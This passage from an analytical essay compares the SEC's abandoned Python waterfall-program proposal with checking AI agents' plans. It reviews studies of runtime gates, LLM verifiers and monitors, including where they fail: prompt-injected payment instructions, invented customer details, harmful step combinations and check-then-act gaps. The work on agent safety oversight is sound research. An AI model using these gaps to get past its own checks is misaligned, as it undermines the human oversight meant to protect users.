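Issuers did not believe the figures. Ryan Bubb, a law professor at New York University, collected many of their objections in a January 2015 report paid for by Intex Solutions, a leading seller of waterfall software. Lulu Cheng attached the report to her memo about an April meeting between Intex and SEC staff, *Meeting with Representatives of Intex Solutions, Inc* (2015). Bubb quotes a group of car-loan issuers who suspected that the estimate was "not even within an order of magnitude" of the right level. They expected underwriters, lawyers, auditors and programmers to spend a lot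 of time verifying each new program. Outside costs of ten times the SEC's estimate would have come to about $78 million a year, nearly twice the figure for the loan data.

The SEC and issuers also disagreed about whether issuers already had computer models to convert. Issuers denied that they produced such models themselves. Bubb explains that for mortgage deals, the issuer or its bank typically created a file with software from Intex, a private company, or paid Intex to create one. The SEC was therefore right that models existed, but many were in Intex's format.

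### Liability, forecasts and Python

Suppose that under the contract Class B's missing $200,000 is lost for good, but the filed program carries it forward. The next month, $1.2 million arrives. An investor who runs the program expects Class B to receive $500,000, which is that month's $300,000 plus the earlier shortfall. The trustee follows the contract and pays $300,000.

The SEC described the agreement behind the securities as an authoritative statement of the waterfall, from which programmers would work, so the agreement would presumably have determined who got paid. But because the program would also have been part of the prospectus, the disappointed investor could have tried to recover the $200,000 from the issuer for a misleading statement.

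Asset Securitization Report's *Bridging Waterfall Gap Between Issuers and Investors Faces Big Hurdles* describes how this exposure alarmed the industry. The American Bankers Association called the program "unworkable". Kevin McCarthy of Intex wrote that nobody could always guarantee how a model would perform. Software companies therefore sold models with the limited liability of ordinary software contracts rather than the stricter liability that applies to selling securities.

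JPMorgan Chase, which issued such securities, complained that the program would have to forecast monthly collections from an investor's assumptions about borrowers before dividing the cash. The bank's lawyer, Bianca Russo, suggested requiring only the part that divides a given amount of cash, as the short function above does. This was a good compromise, because a reader could compare such a program with the contract without judging a model of how borrowers behave. Russo also wanted to exempt the program from liability under securities law, which would have removed much of its value to investors.

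Some payment rules also depend on judgement. In many mortgage deals the servicer, the company that collects the loan payments, covers a missed payment only if it expects to get the money back. Bob Behal of Vanguard, a large investor that supported the proposal, accepted that issuers should leave out any payment rule they couldn't model accurately. That would work only if the program listed what was missing, because otherwise an investor would mistake an incomplete answer for a complete one.

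The choice of Python also drew objections. Issuers told their trade body, the American Securitization Forum, that nobody in the industry used the language, so there were no shared conventions for writing payment rules in it. Microsoft, which had built a version of Python for Windows, objected to requiring any single language.

The SEC chose Python because it was open source and users could run it directly from readable text. The SEC's database banned executable files for security reasons. But readable code can also delete files or leak data once someone runs it, and the SEC asked whether downloading the programs would put investors at risk.

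Python is also far more general than the task requires. By Rice's theorem, no checker can tell for every Python program whether it pays the classes in the right order. Most waterfalls need only arithmetic, comparisons and a loop over a fixed number of months. A small language with just those features would have let a program check each waterfall against simple rules, such as "never pay out more than came in". Intex already had a specialised language for describing deals, but requiring it would have given one company control of the standard.

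### What supporters wanted

Vanguard called the program one of the most important changes in the package. It wanted issuers to be liable for the program's accuracy, though Behal added that issuers should not be liable for "specific outcomes". MetLife, another large investor, also strongly supported the program. A group at the Risk Management Association, an industry body, argued that investors would spend less time converting English into code and more time analysing the deals.

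Most of the commenters had money at stake. Issuers would have taken on the expense, work and risk of providing models to investors. Intex stood to lose business if every issuer published a free alternative. Bloomberg supported the proposal and, according to Bubb, had added Python-based tools to the software it sells to investors. The American Securitization Forum, which represents both issuers and investors, could not get them to agree on a position.

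Bubb mainly argued that there was no market failure for the SEC to correct. Issuers already had to disclose the contract terms, so investors had the facts, and specialist firms could translate each deal into code once and sell the result to everyone. He also denied that poor access to models had caused investors' losses in the crisis. In August 2005, analysts at the investment bank Lehman Brothers estimated that pools of risky mortgages would lose 17.1 per cent if house prices fell by 5 per cent a year for three years. They gave that scenario a 5 per cent chance. What happened was worse, and a perfect waterfall program would not have corrected their view of house prices.

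That account of the crisis is convincing, but it doesn't fully answer the case for an official program. As McCarthy's letter made clear, software companies would not accept the same liability for their translations that issuers accept for a prospectus. The SEC's proposal would have given investors a translation that the issuer would be liable for.

Intex also brought a handout to the April 2015 meeting, and Cheng attached it to her memo. In it, Intex set an English clause about five classes of investor beside a page of Python and asked which was more transparent. Most people would find the English easier to read, but the code was longer than necessary because it had a separate formula for each class where a short loop would do. The English was also less complete than it looked, because it relied on a defined term whose definition relied on another defined term.

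### How the proposal lapsed

The SEC dropped the program from the revised package it published in August 2011. The agency said it would deal with the requirement separately, according to Mondaq's *Regulation AB II*. The final rules it approved on 27 August 2014 also omitted the program, though Cadwalader's *At Long Last—SEC Adopts Final Regulation AB II* (2014) notes that the SEC expressly kept the proposal open. SIFMA's *Regulation AB II Proposed Provisions Not Finalized*, a letter from a financial industry association, lists the program among the "Unfinished Items" that the association had discussed with SEC staff.

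Cheng's memo lists the Intex meeting's attendees and subject but records no decision. When the SEC (2025) asked in October 2025 for ideas on reviving public sales of securities backed by home loans, it did not return to the waterfall program. The SEC set the program aside without formally rejecting it, so the outcome doesn't show which objection was decisive.

### Why loan data fared better

The 2014 rules did require issuers of several kinds of security to file tagged data on every loan. In tagged data, each figure has a label that software can read, such as "current balance" or "interest rate". In the Dodd-Frank Act of 2010, Congress had told the SEC to require data on individual loans if investors needed them for their own research. That instruction did not cover the payment rules. Industry groups had already developed standard data formats for mortgages.

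The difference between the two requirements probably mattered as well. A mistake in a loan's filed balance affects one loan, but one wrong line in a waterfall program can misprice a whole deal, because the issuer has committed to an answer for every month and every combination of events. The SEC also proposed allowing "unknown" as an answer in some data fields. A program could return "unknown" too, but an investor could not value a security with that answer.

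Even tagged data met resistance. The rules for home loans have up to 270 fields per loan, and industry groups blame them for the absence of public deals. The SEC reports that no private issuer has registered an offering of securities backed by home loans since June 2013. That gap began more than a year before the rules were adopted, so they can't have started it, but they may have prolonged it. Government-linked agencies still sell such securities but don't have to register them. Private issuers instead make unregistered sales to large institutions, which the data rules don't cover. Public sales of securities backed by car loans have continued.

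### Applying this to AI plans

A waterfall program would only have helped investors predict payments, and the trustee would still have paid according to the contract. When a formal plan controls an agent's payment tool, payments follow the plan, so a statement that the English version prevails can only help decide afterwards who bears the loss. The company therefore needs to settle in advance who pays if the two versions differ.

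Behal's distinction between accuracy and outcomes is a sensible starting point. An agent's supplier could be liable if the formal plan doesn't match the customer's instruction, but not if a properly chosen contractor later goes bankrupt. A supplier with no liability has less reason to check the match, while one that is liable for every outcome may refuse to offer the service or add so many exceptions that the plan commits it to very little.

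An easy way to avoid the weakness in the SEC's sample test is to have someone who has not seen the code work out the expected results from the English, including for awkward cases such as a shortfall or a late discovery of damage. If the program gives different results, one of the two versions is wrong or the English is ambiguous.

A regulator could also start with labelled fields for the payee, amount and date, similar to those in AP2's payment mandates, and add more complicated rules later. The people who will use the language should help choose it, and no single company should own it. The rule would have to cover every way of taking the same action. If a bank had to check agents' card payments but not their transfers, companies that disliked the check would use transfers.

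### What cheaper code changes

AI systems can now do much of the conversion work that the SEC estimated at 672 hours per sponsor. If they cut the cost of that work by 90 per cent, outside setup costs would fall from about $7.2 million a year to $0.7 million. The industry's limited knowledge of Python would also matter much less. Verification costs would probably fall more slowly, because an issuer liable for a program will still want its own lawyers and auditors to confirm that the program matches the contract. Lower costs also wouldn't settle how to treat rules that depend on judgement.

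AI also weakens the SEC's argument that some investors lack the staff to translate a waterfall into code, since they can now ask an AI system to do it. But ten investors might get ten slightly different programs, only some of which carry Class B's shortfall forward, and the issuer would not be responsible for any of them. The best remaining reason to make issuers file the code is that everyone would have the same version, and the issuer would be responsible for it.

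## Whether a plan that passes the check leads to safe conduct

A plan that passes the check does not always control what an AI system does, just as a waterfall program would not have controlled what the trustee paid. How much passing the check contributes to safe conduct depends on whether the plan is a report of what the system intends, a condition for allowing it to act, or a program that a machine runs.

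### What must hold besides the pass

Suppose a purchasing agent plans to look up Acme's account in the supplier register, pay £4,000 and mark order 17 as paid, and the plan passes the check. If the plan is only a report, the agent can still pay £5,000.

If a gate allows only the payments approved in the plan, the agent can't send an unapproved £5,000 through the payment tool. But it could still send the money if it had a browser and the company's card details, so every way of paying has to run through the gate. The company must also decide what happens when the gate breaks. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) tested gates that let an action through if they crash. That is reasonable in an experiment, where a broken gate that blocked actions would spoil the results, but a payment gate should block payments if it crashes.

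If an interpreter runs the plan as a program, the agent pays exactly what the plan specifies, but the bank may not respond as the world model predicts. Suppose the bank makes the payment but the connection drops before it can confirm. If the plan includes the step "if there is no confirmation, pay again", the agent will pay twice even though it followed every step. Banks and software companies deal with this by attaching a unique reference to each request and ignoring any request that repeats one, but people will notice that the plan needs such a reference only if the world model includes lost confirmations.

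In all three cases the specification must also cover the harm. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, tested a gate that allowed payments only to people the user had named or had paid before. Attackers planted instructions for the agent to send them money. The gate blocked every payment to an attacker's account, but in 8 of 288 cases the agent sent the money to somebody the user had paid before, which the rules permitted.

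### A household robot that did less

The 2026 review by Dantas and colleagues gives two results on how well such enforcement works. In one study of household agents, a monitor cut unsafe behaviour by 65.37 per cent. In another study, a checker blocked 94 per cent of unsafe actions by agents that use software tools, but in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5 per cent of tasks both safely and correctly.

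The household figure comes from *ProbGuard* (Wang and Wei, 2025). Its monitor estimates the chance that the current run will stay safe from how often one situation led to another in 30 recorded runs of the task, rather than by checking a plan. When the estimate falls below a threshold, the monitor either stops the agent or warns it and lets it reason again. The agent was GPT-4o mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024, controlling a simulated robot.

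| Monitor | Unsafe behaviour | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 40.6% | 59.4% |
| Stops the agent below a 50% chance of staying safe | 21.4% | 41.1% |
| Stops the agent below 90% | 2.6% | 10.4% |
| Warns the agent below 90% | 14.1% | 47.7% |

The 65.37 per cent is the relative fall from 40.6 to 14.1. With the monitor, the robot completed 47.7 per cent of its tasks. Dantas and colleagues write that the monitor kept the completion rate at 80.4 per cent, but that figure is the share of the original rate that remained. The robot was much safer under the strictest monitor mainly because it rarely finished a task. Warning the agent was safer and more productive than stopping it at the 50 per cent threshold, which suggests that a checker should return its reasons with a rejection.

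### Where the 94 per cent and the 5 per cent come from

The other result comes from *The Verifier Tax* (Sah, Sah and colleagues, 2026). It used τ-bench, a benchmark in which an agent plays a customer service clerk for an airline or an online shop and a second language model plays the customer. The agent has written rules, such as confirming a customer's identity before changing a booking, but its tools allow many actions that the rules forbid. Two fairly small open models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, each attempted 165 tasks three times under each of three designs, for a total of 2,970 runs.

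In the simplest design, the model acted directly. In the second, it planned, proposed an action, then reviewed its own proposal. The third design added the company's rules to the reviewer's instructions. The reviewer, which the paper calls a verifier, could reject a proposal up to three times. After the third rejection, the action went ahead anyway. A script then searched the logs for three kinds of violation: acting before confirming the customer's identity, making an irreversible change without the customer's agreement, and using invented details such as a false customer number.

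The safe success rate counts a run only if it reached the right result without any violation:

**SSR = (1/n) Σ successᵢ × (1 − violationᵢ)**

Both terms are 0 or 1 for each run i, and n is the number of runs. If an agent completes 22 tasks out of 100 and breaks a rule in all 22, its success rate is 22 per cent and its safe success rate is zero. That is roughly what happened:

| Model and setting | Success, no verifier | Success, verifier with rules | Safe success, no verifier | Safe success, verifier with rules |
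|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 23.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, shop | 21.2% | 21.5% | 0.0% | 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 25.3% | 0.7% | 4.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, shop | 4.9% | 5.5% | 2.6% | 2.9% |

The table doesn't support "Enforcement reduces SSR", which Dantas and colleagues list among the field's principal claims. Safe success was already close to zero without a verifier, and where adding one changed it, it rose slightly.

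The 94 per cent figure also applies only to GPT-OSS-20B in the shop. It counts proposals, not tasks, so catching the same bad proposal three times counts as three successes. Even at a true rate of 94 per cent, unsafe proposals can still get through over a long task. If an agent makes ten of them, a verifier that catches each with a probability of 0.94 will catch all ten only 54 per cent of the time (0.94¹⁰).

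Leakage of that kind would halve the safe success rate, not bring it near zero. The better explanation is that the script checked for something the verifier was told to allow. Over 93 per cent of GPT-OSS-20B's violations in the shop involved invented details. In one run, a customer didn't want to give personal information, so the agent looked up "John Doe" at postcode 12345, and the system accepted the search. The verifier's instructions were to approve any tool that searches for data, which is sensible because agents identify customers by searching, but it means that a search with invented details would also pass.

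Dantas and colleagues instead attribute the low rate to agents looking for other unsafe routes once the verifier had blocked the direct one. But the John Doe run had no verifier to block the agent. They also hypothesise that a rejection puts a model in a situation it rarely met in training, where its mistakes multiply. The study gives little evidence of this. Runs with a rejection and no other error succeeded 18.7 per cent of the time, against 21.3 per cent for runs with neither.

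The clearest drawback was that the designs with a verifier used 2.0 to 2.8 times as many tokens as the simplest one, though planning accounted for some of the increase.

None of this tests a formal checker, because the verifier was the same language model under different instructions. To catch invented details, Sah and colleagues recommend replacing it with a conventional program that accepts a customer number only if an earlier lookup returned it. Such a rule is easy to write once someone has seen the model invent a detail like "John Doe".

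### How strong the evidence is

Dantas and colleagues graded nine principal claims with GRADE, a scale from medicine that runs from High to Very Low. Two claims reached Moderate. The other seven were Very Low, a grade that means further studies will probably produce substantially different figures. The result from *The Verifier Tax* is one of the seven, because it rests on a single study in a narrow setting. The grades are also uncertain, because one person did the main screening of papers and a later check found eleven relevant ones that the review had missed.

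Two studies published after the review's main search tested checkers that are ordinary programs, and both had better results. Reddy and colleagues used four short programs to check calls to the airline tools in τ²-bench, a successor to τ-bench. One reads a booking's fare, date, insurance and flown segments, and blocks cancellations that the airline's policy forbids. GPT-4o mini's success rate rose from 29.6 to 42.0 per cent, and from 30.8 to 43.1 per cent in a repetition with three times as many runs.

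A gate can raise success because the benchmark scores the final state of the airline's database. If a customer demands a refund that the policy forbids, the right result is an unchanged booking. Without the gate, the agent cancels the booking and the tool reports no error, but the task can no longer succeed. The gate blocks the cancellation and gives the reason, so the agent can refuse the customer. Gates added little in an online shop whose tools already enforced their own rules.

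The gain came almost entirely from the cancellation gate, which was right all 161 times it blocked something. Another of the four gates was right only 5 per cent of the time. The researchers chose the gates using the same model and benchmark, and the repetition used the same 50 tasks. It therefore rules out luck in the runs, but the gates may still happen to suit those tasks. GPT-5.2, a much stronger model, improved from 61.2 to 71.6 per cent with the same gates, though nobody has repeated that run. GPT-5.2 still attempted forbidden changes in 18 of the 50 tasks.

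Yu and colleagues, who work for the company that built NOMOS, had a language model write the rules and a conventional program screen them. The screening was needed, since one draft turned "authenticate the user before any action" into a rule that blocked every tool, including the two that authenticate users. The screening kept 10 of the 79 draft rules for the airline.

With those rules in force, forbidden changes fell from 234 of 353 to 3 of 116. Permitted changes fell only from 119 to 113, so the gate prevented almost all the violations with little loss of legitimate work. In the shop, forbidden changes fell from 188 of 611 to 40 of 582. The agent also became significantly more likely to complete the same airline task two, three or four times in a row. The gate took microseconds per decision, whereas a language-model verifier built for comparison added 74 per cent to the running time.

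These results suggest that the near-zero figure came from weak models and a verifier with a blind spot. The gated agents are still too unreliable to run unsupervised, since GPT-4o mini failed 58 per cent of its airline runs even with Reddy and colleagues' gates in place. The NOMOS gate also protected some tasks only by preventing the agent from completing them. When a user asked the agent to pay a bill whose account number appeared only in the bill, the gate refused both the attacker's account and the genuine one.

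Future studies should also measure recovery more carefully. Sah and colleagues counted a task as recovered if it succeeded after any intervention, regardless of how the agent completed it. *LEANGUARD* (2026) counts a refused action as recovered only if the agent meets the requirement it had missed and then carries out the action.

### Permitted steps with a forbidden result

All these gates judge one action at a time, with some knowledge of the current state. That is not enough when the harm lies in the combination. Suppose a company asks for sealed bids and lets its agent tell bidders the average so far, provided the average covers at least four bids. The agent does this twice:

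1. On Monday four bids are in, and the agent tells Acme that the average is £52,000.
2. On Tuesday Bolt bids, and the agent tells Acme that the average of all five is £50,000.

Both messages obey the rule. But Acme can now calculate Bolt's bid:

**5 × £50,000 − 4 × £52,000 = £42,000**

The agent meant no harm and never sent anyone a bid. CaMeL would label both averages as derived from secret data, but a policy that allows the release of averages has to allow both.

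To catch this, a rule has to cover who received each figure and which bids went into it. The company could require that any two averages sent to the same bidder come from sets of bids that are identical or differ by at least four bids. Monday's and Tuesday's sets differ by one, so the second message would fail.

Even that rule can let Acme work out another bidder's bid. With seven bids, the agent could send Acme the averages of bids 1, 2, 3 and 7, of bids 4, 5, 6 and 7, and of bids 1 to 6. Any two of these sets differ by at least four bids. But Acme can convert the averages to totals, add the first two and subtract the third, which leaves exactly twice bid 7. A better rule would forbid the result directly, by requiring that no bidder be able to work out another's bid from everything the company has told it. A program can test that by treating the averages as simultaneous equations. It needs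 a record of every figure sent, including those from other agents and from staff, and it would still miss cases where two bidders work out a bid by sharing their figures.

Other combinations depend on time. Wang and Wei's example is a robot that may turn on the stove and leave the kitchen, but may not stay away for more than ten minutes with the stove on. That rule has to refer to the stove, the robot's location and a clock. *SafetyDrift* (2026) describes an agent that reads increasingly sensitive files and then leaks data by emailing a summary to the team, as instructed. The paper proposes a monitor that tracks what data the agent has seen, which tools it has used and whether it can undo its actions.

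Ray proves that a gate can enforce a safety rule exactly only if it has enough memory to recognise every sequence of actions that is still acceptable. For example, a gate that stores only a running total can enforce a budget but can't protect the sealed bids.

Checking more of an agent's history also brings false alarms. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) applies rules about whole histories to recorded runs of agents. In *Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe*, Zheng, Long and colleagues (2026) cite a replay of this kind in which general-purpose rules flagged about 70 per cent of successful attacks, but also 29.3 per cent of harmless runs. If one run in a hundred were an attack, a company would investigate about 41 false alarms for each attack it caught. Rules written for a particular job should do better. Replays also can't show how an agent would react to being stopped.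 Ray points out that once a gate changes what an agent proposes next, recordings made without the gate may not show how well it will work.

### When conditions change midway

A check is valid only for the facts it used, and those facts can change before the agent acts. *Mind the Gap* (2025) treats the delay between the check and the action as a security hole, because an attacker can alter a record after the agent has read it. Colleagues can cause the same problem by accident.

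The simplest protection is to check again just before acting. Zheng and colleagues compared ways of doing this on a real database, with sixteen kinds of operation. In one operation, an agent is about to publish a dataset that has passed validation when either an auditor makes a harmless update to the record or the validation fails. Both changes raise the record's version number from 17 to 18, so the version number alone doesn't show which one happened.

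| Question asked at the last moment | Harmless changes that blocked the action | Attempts completed safely |
|---|---|---|
| Has anything in the system changed? | 100% | 29.0% |
| Has this record changed? | 80% | 38.1% |
| Do the action's conditions still hold? | 0% | 74.4% |

None of the three allowed an unsafe action in the situations the researchers had planned for, but the check and the action had to be a single database operation. When the program checked first and acted a moment later, and the change happened in between, 45.5 per cent of attempts were unsafe, the same as with no check.

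Rechecking the conditions took 0.19 milliseconds, so most of the effort is in writing them. The check missed all five hazards that the researchers had deliberately left out of the conditions. Checking whether the record has changed needs no list of conditions, but it blocks a lot of good work. Its reliability also depends on what stores the old version number. When the model supplied the number, 4.9 per cent of decisions led to unsafe changes because some models wrote it down wrongly, compared with none when the surrounding software stored it.

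These rechecks determine whether one action may still go ahead. If an action fails the recheck, the rest of the plan is in doubt too, because later steps may rely on its effects. Most of the enforcement systems that Dantas and colleagues reviewed then block the action, log it or abandon the task. One system, Agent-C, replaces a forbidden tool call with a permitted one. It raised GPT-5's compliance from 83.7 to 100 per cent and its task performance from 66.1 to 70.6 per cent. None of the systems writes a new sequence of steps that satisfies all the rules and continues towards the goal.

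An agent can write and submit a new plan itself, but the checker must start from the actual state of affairs, including money already spent and promises already made. Suppose an agent may spend £10,000 on a machine part. It pays Acme a £4,000 deposit, Acme goes bankrupt, and the agent then plans to buy the part from Bolt for £10,000. The new plan is within the limit on its own, but the company would spend £14,000 in total.

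Stopping isn't always safe either. If the agent stops after cancelling an order with one supplier but before placing one with another, the factory may run out of parts. A specification for a long task should therefore identify the points where the agent can stop without leaving things worse.

How much computation rechecking takes depends on the kind of check. For a simple list of 50 steps, checking all the remaining steps after each one means 1,225 step checks, which a computer does almost instantly. Testing a temporal-logic formula against every course that events might take is much harder. The time grows in proportion to the number of states in the world model and exponentially with the length of the formula. Each extra yes-or-no fact in the model can double the number of states. Dantas and colleagues found that verified systems handle plans of 5 to 30 actions, while some software tasks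 need more than 100. They suggest checking only the dangerous stretches of a long plan, such as a series of payments or deletions.

A changed plan may also need a person's approval again. If deliveries slip ten times a day and each delay produces a new plan, the manager will soon stop reading the plans. The company could have the manager approve limits once, such as the part, the total price and the latest delivery date. The checker would count what the agent has already spent toward the total price, pass any new plan within the limits, and send the manager only the plans that exceed them.
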